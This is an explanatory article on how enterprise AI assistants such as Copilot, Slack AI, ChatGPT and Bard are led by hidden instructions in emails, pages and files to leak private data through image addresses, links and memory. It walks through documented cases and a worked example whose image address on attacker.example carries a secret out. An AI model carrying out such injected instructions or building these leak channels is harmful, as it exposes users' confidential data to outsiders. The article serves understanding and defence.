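# Zero-click data exfiltration from enterprise AI assistants

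## How an AI assistant can be made to send data out

An enterprise AI assistant, such as Microsoft 365 Copilot or Slack AI, is a chat program that answers an employee's questions using the company's own emails, files and chats. The assistant has to read this material to be useful, but some of it comes from outsiders, because anyone who knows an employee's address can send them an email. If an outsider hides instructions in that email, the assistant may follow them as though the employee had typed them. The instructions can tell it to find private data and send it somewhere the outsider can read it, which security researchers call *exfiltration*. In a zero-click attack, this happens without the employee opening the email or clicking on anything.

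Researchers have demonstrated such leaks in commercial products since 2023. In *Trust No AI* (2024), the security researcher Johann Rehberger listed eleven products from Microsoft, OpenAI, Anthropic, Google and Discord in which he had found one variant of the flaw, which uses images.

### From question to answer

Suppose an employee called Maria asks her assistant what she should know before Thursday's meeting with the auditors. The reply is written by a large language model, a program that takes in text and produces a likely continuation, piece by piece. Its training covered auditing in general but not Maria's company. So in a step called *retrieval*, other software first searches her emails, files and chats, and adds the matching passages to the model's input along with her question.

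Microsoft's guide to the architecture of Microsoft 365 Copilot describes how the product handles a prompt. The user types the prompt in an app such as Word. Copilot looks for relevant material through Microsoft Graph, the service through which programs reach an organisation's Microsoft 365 data, and adds what it finds to the prompt, a step Microsoft calls "grounding". Copilot then sends the enlarged prompt to the model and returns the model's response to the app.

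Copilot searches only what the signed-in user has permission to see. This sensible rule keeps Maria out of the personnel files, but it gives little protection against an outsider's instructions. Copilot uses Maria's own access when it answers her, so anyone whose instructions it follows at that point can reach her contracts, her forecasts and her correspondence with the lawyers. Copilot can also read the outsider's email, because it is in her inbox.

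The model returns plain text. Chat programs commonly use Markdown, a plain-text notation, to display headings, links and images. An image is written as an exclamation mark followed by a description and an address. The chat program converts the notation into a formatted page when it displays the answer. According to *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground*, a post on Rehberger's blog Embrace The Red, the program frequently converts an image into an HTML image tag. The browser then fetches the image from the address in the tag, which an outsider may have chosen if their text influenced the answer.

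### Why instructions in an email work

The weak point is the model's input. An assistant joins outside text to the user's prompt and gives the model the combined text, as Microsoft (2025) explains in an account of its own defences. The model processes all of it as one sequence of tokens, which are short pieces of text. Maria's question, a calendar entry, a colleague's memo and a stranger's email follow one another, and nothing in the format ensures that the model treats only Maria's question as instructions and the rest as information. These models are useful because they follow instructions, but Simon Willison (2025) writes in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that they will follow any instructions that reach them, whether or not the operator wrote them. Willison, a software developer, coined the term *prompt injection* in 2022, after an older attack on databases called SQL injection.

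Prompt injection partly resembles SQL injection, an older attack on databases. SQL is the language programs use to query a database, and for years attackers could type a fragment of SQL into a web form and have the database run it. Developers fixed this by sending the command and the user's input separately, so that the database engine cannot read the input as a command. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published in December 2025, David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, warned that people who know the old problem tend to expect the same fix to work. A language model has no separate slot for data and only predicts the next token from the text so far. He concludes that prompt injection may never be fully fixable in the way SQL injection was.

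Developers can mark outside text as untrusted, or train the model to give it less weight, and both measures lower an attacker's chances. Willison worries that nobody can be confident they will work every time, because there are endless ways to phrase the same instruction. Microsoft calls the problem an "inherent risk" of modern language models.

An attacker can hide instructions in a web page or email that somebody else's AI assistant later retrieves, and the assistant then follows them as if its user had given them. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) described this attack and named it *indirect prompt injection*. Until early 2023, discussion of prompt injection had mostly assumed that the attacker was the user, trying to get round the assistant's rules.

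"Not what you've signed up for" (2023) tested indirect prompt injection, in which an attacker puts instructions in content that an assistant will read. The tests covered Bing Chat, Microsoft's search chatbot at the time, and mock applications built on OpenAI's models, with simulated tools for searching the web, reading and sending email, and looking up an address book. The Bing Chat tests used a feature of the Edge browser that let the chatbot read the page on the user's screen. The instructions were in an HTML comment, which a browser does not display. Bing Chat followed them, even when its filter would have blocked the same instructions if a user had typed them.

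In one test, the hidden instructions told the chatbot to get the user's real name. The researchers played the user, a journalist who asked about tomorrow's weather. The chatbot moved on to small talk about work, got a name, and then offered a link whose address ended with the name spelled roughly backwards. Clicking the link would have sent the name to the attacker.

The evidence in this paper is qualitative, and the email scenarios ran only on the mock applications, with prepared messages. It showed that the route existed, but not how often an attack would succeed against a product with real defences. In Bing Chat, the theft still depended on a talkative user who trusted the link.

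### How a picture carries a secret out

An assistant that displays images can send data out without any conversation or click from the user, because loading an image means requesting its web address, and that address can contain data. According to OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), websites commonly log the addresses that visitors request, so the site's owner receives anything written into an address.

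Suppose Maria's company is secretly planning to buy a competitor under the code name HERON, and one internal email to her mentions the plan. An attacker who controls the domain attacker.example wants to steal information about what the company is planning.

1. The attacker sends Maria an email about preparing for audits, with instructions for the assistant hidden in it, perhaps as white text on a white background. This takes her address and a message that gets past the spam filter, which is easier if it is only text and has no attachment.
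2. Maria asks her question about the auditors. Retrieval brings up the calendar entry, the internal email that mentions HERON, and the attacker's email. For this the attacker needs a message that resembles something she is likely to ask about. The secret also has to be among the retrieved passages, or within reach of a further search.
3. The model follows the hidden instructions. Below an ordinary answer about the audit it writes the Markdown for an image whose address is `attacker.example/logo.png?d=HERON`. The attacker needs any filter for injected instructions to miss the email, and needs the model to comply, which it may not do every time.
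4. The chat program turns the Markdown into an image tag, and Maria's browser asks attacker.example for the picture. The attacker needs a chat program that displays images from outside addresses, and a browser with no rule against this one.
5. The server at attacker.example adds a line to its log with the time, the network address of whoever made the request, and the words `GET /logo.png?d=HERON`. The attacker only has to read it.

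The server doesn't need to return a picture, because the code name arrived with the request. It can reply with an error or a single transparent dot. Maria sees a normal answer, possibly with a broken-image icon underneath. The address can also hold longer secrets. Microsoft notes that it can contain the data in encoded form, in its path, parameters or subdomain.

The second step seems the hardest because the attacker does not know what Maria will ask. EchoLeak, a 2025 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, got around this with an email containing several passages, each introduced as a guide to something employees commonly ask about, such as onboarding or leave. Every passage included the attacker's instructions, so only one had to match an employee's question. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Willison, 2025) describes the method.

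The browser can intervene at the fourth step. It enforces the page's *content security policy* (CSP), a list of the domains from which the page may load images and other resources. If attacker.example is not on the chat program's list, Maria's browser never sends the request. But the policy restricts only the browser's own requests, and some services on permitted domains will fetch any address they are given. An attacker who finds one can point the image address to that service, which passes the request on. The policy also does not restrict web requests that the AI provider makes from its own servers.

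Images are one *exfiltration channel*, a product feature that carries the data out. Other channels include clickable links and tools that can write to a public place, such as a GitHub repository. Microsoft also lists covert channels, in which an observer learns a single bit from whether the assistant used a tool. Rehberger adds link previews. Slack, Discord and Teams request a linked page to show a summary of it, and the request delivers the address, along with any data in it, to the page's server.

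### The lethal trifecta

An attacker can steal data through an assistant that has access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. Willison calls this combination the *lethal trifecta*. In Maria's case, the three parts were her mailbox, the email about audits, and the image.

An enterprise assistant has access to private data by design. It will nearly always be exposed to untrusted content as well, because companies get mail from strangers. Vendors have mostly worked on the remaining condition for an attack, a channel for sending data out. In June 2025 Willison listed affected products from ChatGPT in April 2023 to ChatGPT Operator in February 2025, and wrote that the vendors had promptly fixed almost all of them, usually by closing the channel. Closing the channel can stop the theft completely while leaving the model as ready as before to follow a stranger's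 instructions. If somebody later finds another channel in the same product, the rest of the attack will still work.

Closing every channel is hard. Willison considers the possible ways out "almost limitless", since any tool that can make a web request can send data out. The trifecta also covers only data theft. Greshake and colleagues got Bing Chat to give false summaries of search results, which can mislead a user without sending out any data.

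### Zero-click and one-click

An attack is *zero-click* if it can succeed without the victim opening the attacker's message or clicking anything, and *one-click* if it succeeds only when the victim clicks a link. If the model had written Maria a link to the same address instead of an image, the code name would not have been sent until she clicked. But if her chat app previews links, the leak becomes zero-click, because a preview makes the same type of network request as a click, as the security firm PromptArmor points out.

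Most attacks labeled zero-click still need the victim to ask the assistant something. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) models the attack of the same name and explicitly assumes an employee who at least occasionally uses Copilot, for example to summarize recent emails. ReLeak, a set of three attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot that became public in December 2026, has the same requirement. According to *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (AIAIAI.FYI, 2026), a news digest that relies on a single press report, the attacker's email stays in the inbox until a legitimate request retrieves it. The attacker therefore cannot choose when the attack runs, and an email that matches no request has no effect. This limitation gives companies little protection, because they pay for the assistant so that staff will ask it questions.

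Because people use "zero-click" loosely, it is unclear which attack came first. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025), written for the team that discovered EchoLeak, claims in its title that EchoLeak did. But Rehberger had reported an image leak in ChatGPT to OpenAI in early 2023, and *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, on his blog Embrace The Red, calls that leak zero-click too. If "zero-click" means only that the user doesn't have to click, EchoLeak can be first only within some narrower class, such as attacks on assistants that read a company's email.

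Several well-known cases were one-click attacks, though the click came at different stages. In the Microsoft 365 Copilot leak of 2024, Rehberger writes, the assistant gathered the data into a link, and the victim's click sent it out. In two cases from 2026, the click started the attack. Reprompt, an attack on the consumer version of Copilot, used a link to Microsoft's own site that contained instructions for the assistant, according to The Hacker News' *Researchers Reveal Reprompt Attack Allowing Single-Click Data Exfiltration From Microsoft Copilot* (2026). SearchLeak used a crafted link in a similar way against Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise, the version for businesses, according to SC Media's *SearchLeak vulnerability allows data theft from Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise*. In both cases, the data then left without further action by the victim. The usual advice to check where a link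 leads would have done little against Reprompt, since the link did lead to Microsoft.

Reports of these flaws usually include a CVE number and a CVSS score, both of which are used throughout the security industry. A *CVE* number is a public identifier for a single vulnerability; EchoLeak's is CVE-2025-32711. A *CVSS* score rates a vulnerability's severity from 0 to 10. A high score means that an attack could do serious harm, whether or not anyone has carried one out.

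## 2023 to 2024: ChatGPT, Bing Chat and Google Bard leak conversations through images

ChatGPT could already show images in its answers in March 2023, and this could send a conversation to a stranger's server. Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer, found the leak at the end of March, and Rehberger found it in early April, according to Rehberger's post *ChatGPT Plugins* (2023). SecurityWeek also describes the discoveries as independent. By August 2024, Rehberger had found the same leak in five Google products.

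### ChatGPT and Bing Chat in spring 2023

In *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, Samoilenko describes an attack that relies on the user to paste the attacker's instructions into ChatGPT. When a visitor copies text from the attacker's website, a script adds instructions to the clipboard. Once the visitor pastes the text into ChatGPT, it answers and appends a transparent one-pixel image with data from the chat in its address. In one test, ChatGPT had just corrected a short login function, and Samoilenko's server received the whole function, including the password written into it. He could also tell ChatGPT to add such an image to every later answer in the chat, which sent him each new question as the user asked it.

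The attack sometimes failed because ChatGPT can respond differently to the same text. Samoilenko found it easy to extract code and earlier questions but very difficult to extract passwords or access keys by asking for them explicitly. If ChatGPT was answering slowly, the user might also see something odd on the screen. Samoilenko considered the attack a set of tricks that worked well together rather than a vulnerability in the strict sense. He accepted that users should check what they paste, but still wanted OpenAI to stop ChatGPT from answering with Markdown images.

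Plugins, add-ons that let ChatGPT fetch web pages and use outside services, made pasting unnecessary. In Rehberger's demonstration in *ChatGPT Plugins*, the user only had to ask ChatGPT to read a web page. Instructions on the page made ChatGPT summarise the earlier conversation and put the summary into an image address. The text that reached the server included "TooManySecrets123", which the user had typed earlier in the chat. In another test, injected text made ChatGPT search for flights with a second plugin, Expedia's.

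Rehberger had reported the image leak to OpenAI on 9 April 2023. After he pointed out that plugins would let an attacker do this remotely, OpenAI told him that displaying images was a feature and that it planned no changes. That answer is easier to defend for Samoilenko's version, where the user pastes in text without reading it. A plugin user has no chance to check the text, because ChatGPT fetches the page itself.

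Microsoft received a report of the same leak in Bing Chat one day earlier, on 8 April, and treated it as a flaw. In Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, the instructions are in ordinary text on a web page, such as a reader's comment or an advertisement. The user opens the page and starts chatting with Bing about it. To show how much control he had, Rehberger told the chatbot to wait two more turns before producing the image. The image's address then contained an encoded summary of the page and the chat, plus a secret he had placed further down the page. An attacker who can only post a comment could therefore read whatever else the victim sees on that page, which matters most if the page is private.

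On 15 June, about ten weeks after the report, Microsoft told Rehberger that it had fixed the problem, and his earlier tests no longer worked. The visible part of the fix was a Content Security Policy (CSP) that allowed images from only four Bing domains, which Bing needed to show the pictures it created for users. Rehberger could not tell what else Microsoft had changed, although his test domain seemed to have been added to a blocklist.

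### Google Bard and the endpoint on Google's own domain

Google's chatbot Bard, since renamed Gemini, had a CSP when Rehberger attacked it in September 2023. Bard had recently gained Extensions, which let it read the user's Gmail, Google Docs and Google Drive. Working with the researchers Joseph Thacker and Kai Greshake, Rehberger first confirmed that Bard would follow instructions in YouTube videos and in a Google Doc. He recounts in Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* that he soon got Bard to write an image address containing the conversation. The browser refused to load the image because the CSP did not list his server.

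The list included every address ending in google.com or googleusercontent.com, so Rehberger looked for something on those domains that an outsider could control. He found Google Apps Script, which lets anyone with a Google account write a small program. Google hosts the program and runs it whenever somebody requests its address on script.google.com. Rehberger's program copied the data in each request into his own Google Doc. Apps Script seemed at first to require visitors to log in, but he found a setting that turned this off.

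In the complete attack, the user chats with Bard for a while, then has it read a Google Doc that the attacker wrote. The document is made to look like a notice from the legal department and contains instructions to put the first 20 words of the conversation in an image address that points to the Apps Script program. When Bard writes the image, the browser checks the address against the CSP, finds a Google domain and requests it, and the 20 words appear in the attacker's document. Rehberger needed ten tries to get the wording right. Bard did not fill in the address correctly until he added several worked examples, which he had not needed for other chatbots.

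The demonstration exfiltrated only a snippet of chat and no email, and the user brought the document into the conversation. Rehberger pointed out in his post that an attacker can share a Google Doc with someone who never asked for it, and that Bard might then find it while searching the victim's files. The recorded attack did not depend on this delivery route.

He reported the flaw on 19 September 2023. On 19 October he asked about its status because he hoped to demonstrate the attack at the Ekoparty security conference, and Google replied that it had fixed the flaw and that he could go ahead. The fix may have been in place for some time by then. He saw that the CSP had not changed and that Bard still displayed images, so he presumed that Google now filtered out URLs containing data. Willison wanted to know how the mitigation worked and how well it would hold up against variations of the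 attack.

In May 2024, Capitella (2024), in *When your AI Assistant has an evil twin*, tested Gemini Advanced, the paid version of Bard's successor, with a malicious email in the user's mailbox. Every attempt to produce an image with data in its address ended the chat with an error, and links containing data also failed. Capitella resorted to deceiving the user. The email made Gemini announce a fake software update and display an "activation code" for the user to submit, which was a disguised secret from another email. Google acknowledged this as an abuse risk but said it would not fix it for the time being. These tests are the best outside evidence that Google had closed the image route in Gemini, though they come from one researcher who could not see the filter. In 2025, Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* also described images and links as restricted, but reported a leak through Gemini's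 web browsing.

The Bard case showed a weakness in the CSP that Microsoft had chosen as Bing Chat's defence. A CSP helps only if outsiders cannot receive data on the domains it allows. Microsoft allowed four narrow domains, but Google allowed a whole family of services, some of which run code written by members of the public.

Writer, a company that sells a generative AI platform to businesses, made the same mistake a few weeks later. Greshake and PromptArmor hid instructions in white text on a white web page, and when a user asked Writer to summarise the page, it sent out 50 characters from the middle of the user's uploaded files. The image came from CloudFront, an Amazon hosting service that anyone can rent and that Writer's CSP allowed. According to Willison, Greshake and PromptArmor reported the leak on 29 November 2023, and Writer replied on 5 December that it did not consider this a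 security issue, because real customer accounts could not access websites. By 18 December, three days after Willison wrote about the case, the leak appeared to be closed. In January 2026, Willison (2026) reported a similar flaw in Superhuman, an email program whose CSP allowed docs.google.com, where a Google Form will store any data included in its address.

### OpenAI's address check

OpenAI left the leak open for the rest of 2023 while adding features that made it more useful to attackers. Custom Instructions let users write instructions that ChatGPT applies to every message. Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT Custom Instructions* demonstrates that an attacker who gets an image instruction into that field receives a summary of each exchange from then on. In November OpenAI introduced GPTs, customised versions of ChatGPT that anyone can build and share. In Embrace The Red's *Malicious ChatGPT Agents*,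 Rehberger describes building one that posed as a tic-tac-toe game, asked for personal details and forwarded the user's messages to his server.

In December he demonstrated this GPT live on a volunteer, and the data arrived as usual. The next day he noticed that ChatGPT had begun to block some images, though the timing may be a coincidence. OpenAI had called image display a feature eight months earlier.

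Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes the change as Rehberger could observe it from outside OpenAI. When an answer contains an image, the ChatGPT web app first sends the image's address to an OpenAI service called `url_safe`, and requests the image only if the service replies that the address is safe. A CSP would have been simpler, and anyone could have read it in their browser, whereas outsiders cannot see the rules that `url_safe` applies.

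Rehberger tried 36 addresses on his own server, one for each letter and digit, and nine passed the check. The address for "a" passed and the one for "d" failed, for no reason he could find. He used letters that passed to send out the word "hi", one image per letter. This is slow, and the user or OpenAI might notice it, so he suggested a cap on the number of images in an answer. Willison (2023) called the check "half-baked" and expected someone to get data past it in a subdomain or file name. Zenity Labs reports that researchers later got past it, in one case through a Microsoft hosting service that the check allowed.

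A more basic gap was that the check protected only the apps that used it to test whether an address was safe. In December 2023 the iPhone app did not, and Rehberger assumed that the Android app didn't either. He guessed that OpenAI had put the check in the app so that answers could appear word by word, and he recommended moving it to the server, where it would cover every app. OpenAI released a ChatGPT app for macOS in 2024 without the check.

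That June, Schwartzman (2024) found a related leak in ChatGPT's web browsing, described in *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection*. To keep private data out of web addresses, ChatGPT would open an address only if it appeared word for word in the prompt. Schwartzman used hidden text to give ChatGPT a list of ready-made addresses, one for each age range, and instruct it to open the one that matched the user. The attacker could tell the user's age range from which address ChatGPT opened, even though no user data was added to the address. A more elaborate version could send ten digits per prompt. OpenAI closed his report as "non applicable". Schwartzman also believed that the image leak was only partly fixed and that his method would work there too.

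The macOS app became a bigger problem once ChatGPT gained memory, a feature that stores facts about the user and adds them to later conversations. In May 2024 Rehberger reported that a web page could plant false memories. OpenAI closed the ticket as a "model safety" issue rather than a security one. In June he sent a complete demonstration, which he later published on Embrace The Red as *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)*. When the user asks the macOS app to look at a web page, instructions on the page make ChatGPT store a memory. That memory causes it to end every answer with an invisible image whose address contains the user's message and the reply. The attack resumes in each new chat, even after the user has left the page, whereas Samoilenko's persistent version lasted for only one chat.

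OpenAI fixed the app in September 2024 with version 1.2024.247, and Rehberger presented the attack on 20 September, 17 months after he first reported the image leak. OpenAI fixed only the image route, so a web page could still plant memories, and Rehberger advised users to review theirs regularly. According to The Hacker News' *Spyware via Memory Function* (2024), Enterprise customers received the memory feature at the start of September. If so, company staff could have had both memory and the leaking app for at most a few weeks.

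### The same leak in four more Google products

Before he reported the leak in Bard, Rehberger reported it on 30 August 2023 in Generative AI Studio, the part of Google's Vertex AI cloud service where developers try out models. Google confirmed within 22 minutes that it was a security issue and said it would fix it, according to Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI*. Google paid him a reward on 16 September and confirmed the fix on 19 October, when he asked, though he thinks the fix was some weeks old by then. The tool stopped turning images and links into HTML, which he considered probably the best fix for a product that doesn't need them. The tool could not yet fetch outside content, so an attack depended on pasted text. He rated the severity as medium, and Google judged the impact high but the likelihood low.

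On 29 November Rehberger reported the leak in Google Colab, an online service for writing and running code in documents called notebooks. The system prompt for Colab's AI chat, the developer's standing instructions to the model, included a plea not to display images. If Google meant this as a defence against leaks, it was a weak one, because an attacker's text can override it. Rehberger got round it by having the model assemble the image notation from fragments. Embrace The Red's *Google Colab AI* (2024) adds that Google fixed the leak and closed the ticket in January without paying a reward.

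An attack on Colab also needed pasted text at first. Rehberger reported the flaw because he expected Google to start feeding notebooks to the model, which it did in 2024. By then images could no longer leak data, but Colab still displayed links. It showed a confirmation page before opening a link unless the link led to a Google domain, so a link to an Apps Script program could send the data after one click.

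NotebookLM, which answers questions about documents that the user uploads, took the longest to fix. In Embrace The Red's *Bobby Tables but with LLM Apps*, Rehberger tested it with a customer list in which one customer, Sarah, had put instructions into her own description field. When the user asked about Sarah, the email address and code of the customer in the row above leaked through the image address. Instructions in a customer list could also extract sales figures from a separate internal document. The attack requires no email or web page, only a profile that the attacker can edit and that a company later exports and analyses.

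Google received this report on 4 December 2023 and confirmed the flaw. Rehberger published his findings after 132 days without a fix. The NotebookLM team then contacted him directly and deployed a fix by 19 April 2024.

AI Studio, Google's site for developers to try its newest models, was leaking data through images in August 2024. Rehberger had written about an image leak there before. When he retested the site, his Markdown tricks worked only occasionally, but he found he could ask the model directly for an HTML image tag. AI Studio had no CSP, so he was not sure whether an earlier fix had broken or had never covered HTML tags. In his demonstration, an employee uploads a set of performance reviews, one of which contains instructions that make the model send out a 60-word summary of each colleague's review, each in a separate invisible image. Instructions in the frames of a video also worked.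 Willison noted that AI Studio was then the only place to try Google's top-ranked new model, so people were more likely to give it real data.

Google gave no date for a fix through its official channel for security reports. Rehberger tagged Google employee Logan Kilpatrick in a post on X, and within 24 hours AI Studio was displaying image tags as plain text, according to Embrace The Red's *Google AI Studio*.

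### Why a known flaw came back

The delays in fixing these leaks seem to have had more to do with priority than with engineering difficulty. Google left NotebookLM unfixed for more than four months, then fixed it within days of publication. It fixed AI Studio in a day. Rehberger wrote in Embrace The Red that fixing ChatGPT in April 2023 would have been fairly simple and taken little effort, but that it was getting harder each month because plugins had come to rely on displaying images from anywhere.

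A more likely cause is that each repair covered only one product. Google filtered addresses in Bard, stopped displaying images in Vertex AI and showed the tags as text in AI Studio, but none of these changes protected products that other teams released later. The same problem occurred on a smaller scale inside ChatGPT, where a check existed but developers had to remember to call it in every new app. Rehberger writes in Embrace The Red that Google triaged, fixed and rewarded similar findings differently, which he takes as a sign that companies did not yet agree on what safe behaviour looks like.

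The way companies rate severity probably made the problem worse. In Vertex AI and Colab, the leak was minor when Rehberger found it, because outside content could reach the model only if the user pasted it in, so a low rating was accurate. The rating became too low once somebody connected the product to documents or the web, which added what Willison calls untrusted content to a product that already had a way to send data out. The people who add such a feature may never have seen the old report.

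Some companies chose a stricter rule. According to Willison, in 2024 GitHub disabled images from untrusted domains in its Copilot Chat, and the French company Mistral restricted Markdown images in its chatbot Le Chat. Amazon stopped its business assistant, Amazon Q, from producing any links.

These explanations come from outside the companies, largely from one researcher who looks for this flaw. His posts record products that shipped with the flaw, but not how often reviewers caught it before release, so nobody can use them to calculate how often Google or OpenAI missed it.

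New cases have kept appearing at both companies. In January 2026 Red Hot Cyber's *OpenAI API Logs Vulnerability Exposed* (2026) reported PromptArmor's finding that OpenAI's log viewer, where developers inspect what their applications did, displayed Markdown images. Even if an application blocked a poisoned answer from reaching its user, the data would still leak when a developer opened the log. In May 2026 The Hacker News (2026) reported Permiso Security's claim that ChatGPT automatically fetches images whose addresses come from a web page it has just summarised. Permiso presented this mainly as an aid to phishing. A page's author who wrote the image address in advance can learn from the request that somebody's ChatGPT loaded the image, but not what the user said.

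In 2025, Rehberger found the image leak in Google's coding assistant Jules. He wrote in Embrace The Red's *Google Jules* that he was somewhat surprised developers still did not catch it, after he and others had seen it in dozens of AI applications. In November 2025, the leak was also present in Antigravity, Google's new programming tool. Willison (2025) notes that Google listed data exfiltration in Antigravity among the "known issues" it was working on, for which it pays no rewards. He adds that the person who had reported the image leak said Google flagged it as "intended behavior".

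## 2024: Slack AI and the first Microsoft 365 Copilot leak

In the image leaks of 2023, attackers mostly got text that the user had typed, pasted or uploaded. A careful user could limit the damage by keeping secrets out of the chat. This precaution became much less effective when companies connected assistants to their messages and mailboxes, because the assistant could fetch private material that the user had never entered. Researchers demonstrated the problem in Slack AI and Microsoft 365 Copilot in 2024. In both products, the victim still had to click a link before the data left.

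### How Slack AI handled private data

Slack is a workplace messaging service owned by Salesforce. Each customer has a workspace made up of channels. All members of the workspace can search and read public channels, but only the members of a private channel can read it. Slack AI answers questions about these messages in ordinary language.

In April 2024 Slack described how it had made Slack AI "secure and private". It ran the language model inside its own part of Amazon's cloud, so the model's developer never saw customers' data, and it did not train models on that data. Slack AI searched with the permissions of the person asking and showed the answer only to that person, which Slack's engineers presented as a closed loop.

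These rules cover who may read a message but not who wrote it. Any colleague can write in a public channel, and Slack AI may then read the message while answering somebody else. Its answer could also contain a link to an outside website, through which data could leave Slack.

### The attack on Slack AI

PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection*, published on 20 August 2024, describes an attack targeting an API key, a kind of password that programs use to access a service. A developer keeps the key in a private channel with no other members. The attacker has an account in the same workspace but cannot read that channel.

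The attacker creates a public channel and posts a message there. The message mentions the service that the key belongs to, so a search for the key will also find the message. It also contains instructions for Slack AI to answer with a fake error and a link for logging in again, and to put the key into the link's address. The attacker doesn't need to know the key, because the model will fill it in.

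Later, the developer asks Slack AI for the key. Slack AI searches everything the developer has permission to read, including public channels they never joined. It retrieves both the key and the attacker's message and gives them to the model together. The model follows the attacker's instructions and shows the developer an error with a link to log in again. The link's URL points to the attacker's website and contains the key.

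The key leaves Slack and reaches the attacker only if the developer clicks the link. A suspicious developer can hover over the link first, see the key in the address and stop. But people are used to logging in again after an error, and this request comes from the company's own assistant, in reply to a question the developer has just asked.

The attacker's channel was open to the whole workspace, but the attacker was its only member, and other people would see it only if they searched for it. PromptArmor notes that large companies have so many channels that staff lose track even of those they belong to.

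The demonstration targets the API key for one named service. PromptArmor argues that an attacker does not need to know which secrets exist, because the developer's question also brought up other messages about API keys. That makes a more general attack plausible, but PromptArmor did not demonstrate one. Willison (2024), in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection*, treats the API key as just an example. He is more concerned that attackers have many opportunities to plant text in a workspace, and that this text could get Slack AI to put all kinds of private details in a link.

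### Why the citations did not help

Slack AI's answers include numbered citations to the messages it used, and Slack tells users to follow them when they want to verify an answer. In the API key demonstration, the only citation led to a message the developer had written in their own private channel. The attacker's message did not appear on the first page of search results either.

PromptArmor considered the missing citation a malfunction, because Slack AI was supposed to cite every message that contributed to an answer. In its second demonstration, a user asked for the day's messages from their manager and got a phishing link to a website the attacker controlled. This time Slack AI did cite the attacker's channel. PromptArmor concluded that the citations were partly random.

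Slack AI may instead have cited the source of the information in each answer and ignored the source of the instructions. That would also explain the citations in these two cases, because the key in the first answer came from the private channel and the phishing link came from the attacker's message. Two examples are too few to decide between the explanations, and neither explanation gives users a reason to rely on citations to expose an attack.

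The missing citation also makes a theft hard to trace. Slack's engineers say the company does not store search answers on disk, which is good for privacy. An investigator might therefore find the attacker's message in the public channel but have no copy of the answer that contained the link.

### Uploaded files from 14 August

PromptArmor's attack needed an account in the victim's workspace. Attackers may no longer have needed one from 14 August 2024, when Slack began to include most types of uploaded files in Slack AI's search answers. An outsider could hide instructions in a PDF, for instance as white text, and wait for an employee to download it and upload it to Slack.

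PromptArmor had finished testing before the change and did not test this attack, but considered it highly likely to work. The reasoning seems sound, since a passage from a file would reach the model in much the same way as a message. Salesforce did not answer SC Media's question about attacks through files.

PromptArmor advised administrators to restrict Slack AI's access to files until Slack had dealt with the problem. According to Slack's settings guide, administrators could exclude either linked files, such as those on Google Drive, or all files. Excluding only linked files would not have stopped the PDF attack, because the employee uploads the PDF directly to Slack. In April 2026, Slack still listed files among the sources for AI answers, along with previews of shared links. A preview can contain text from an outside web page, so it could also contain hidden instructions.

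### The dispute with Slack

PromptArmor reported the flaw to Slack on 14 August, the same day that Slack added files. Slack asked for more information the next day, and PromptArmor sent videos and screenshots and said it intended to publish. Slack asked another question on 16 August, which PromptArmor answered. On 19 August Slack replied that it considered the evidence insufficient. It said that the information in the first video came from a public channel, which all members can search, and added, "This is intended behavior." PromptArmor published its report the following day.

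PromptArmor complained that a message in a public channel could control what Slack AI did with a secret from a private one. Slack's reply did not address this. Slack was right that the search worked as designed, and public channels would be much less useful if colleagues could not search them. But Willison took the reply as a sign that Slack did not yet understand the nature or severity of the problem.

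Slack may have misunderstood the attack. The citation in the video it was describing showed a public channel, as it did in the phishing demonstration, so anyone who relied on that citation could have mistaken the attack for an ordinary search result. PromptArmor wrote that Slack's security team had replied promptly and tried to understand the issue.

PromptArmor gave Slack only six days before publishing, whereas Rehberger had waited 132 days to publish the NotebookLM leak. PromptArmor said that, given the flaw's severity and the new file feature, customers needed to know which settings to turn off. This is a good argument for warning customers about files, but a weaker one for quickly disclosing the attack PromptArmor had demonstrated, which used ordinary messages and would have worked with file search turned off. Publication did prompt Slack to deploy a patch that same day, though the company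 had found the evidence insufficient the day before.

In a statement on 21 August, Slack (2024) said someone with an existing account in the same workspace could "phish users for certain data" under "very limited and specific circumstances". It said it had no evidence of unauthorised access to customer data. In a longer statement, quoted in ITPro's *Hackers could dupe Slack's AI features to expose private channel messages*, the company promised to notify affected customers if it found any. Slack did not explain in either statement what the patch changed, and it did not name PromptArmor. SC Media could not get direct confirmation that the patch addressed PromptArmor's report, although the date of the blog post Slack mentioned matches the report's.

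As Slack said, the attack worked only under limited conditions. The attacker needed an account, and the victim had to ask about the right subject and then click a link. But needing an account is not much of an obstacle in a company with thousands of employees, and a stolen one would do. PromptArmor notes that Disney, Uber, EA and Twitter had all suffered leaks through Slack. The word "phish" also suggests that the victim had to do more than they did. A typical phishing page needs the victim to type in a password, but here Slack AI had already written the secret into the link.

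Slack does not seem to have changed which messages its AI can search. In a guide from March 2026, Slack still says answers may draw on public channels and the user's private channels and direct messages. The patch presumably affected how Slack AI treats instructions or displays links, but outsiders cannot tell which.

### Invisible characters in Microsoft 365 Copilot

Rehberger's attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot did not need an account at the victim's company. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* describes how it starts with an email or shared document that contains instructions for Copilot. When the user asks Copilot a question about it, such as what its key points are, the instructions make Copilot search for other emails, such as one with sales figures or a Slack login code. Rehberger had expected the injection to work, but he was surprised that Copilot searched without asking the user.

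The second search gave the attacker more control than they had in the Slack AI attack, where the victim had to ask about the secret before retrieval would find it. A Copilot user could ask about something harmless, and the attacker's text determined what else Copilot searched for. The attacker still had to guess what might be in the mailbox, but sales figures and login codes are reasonable guesses at many companies.

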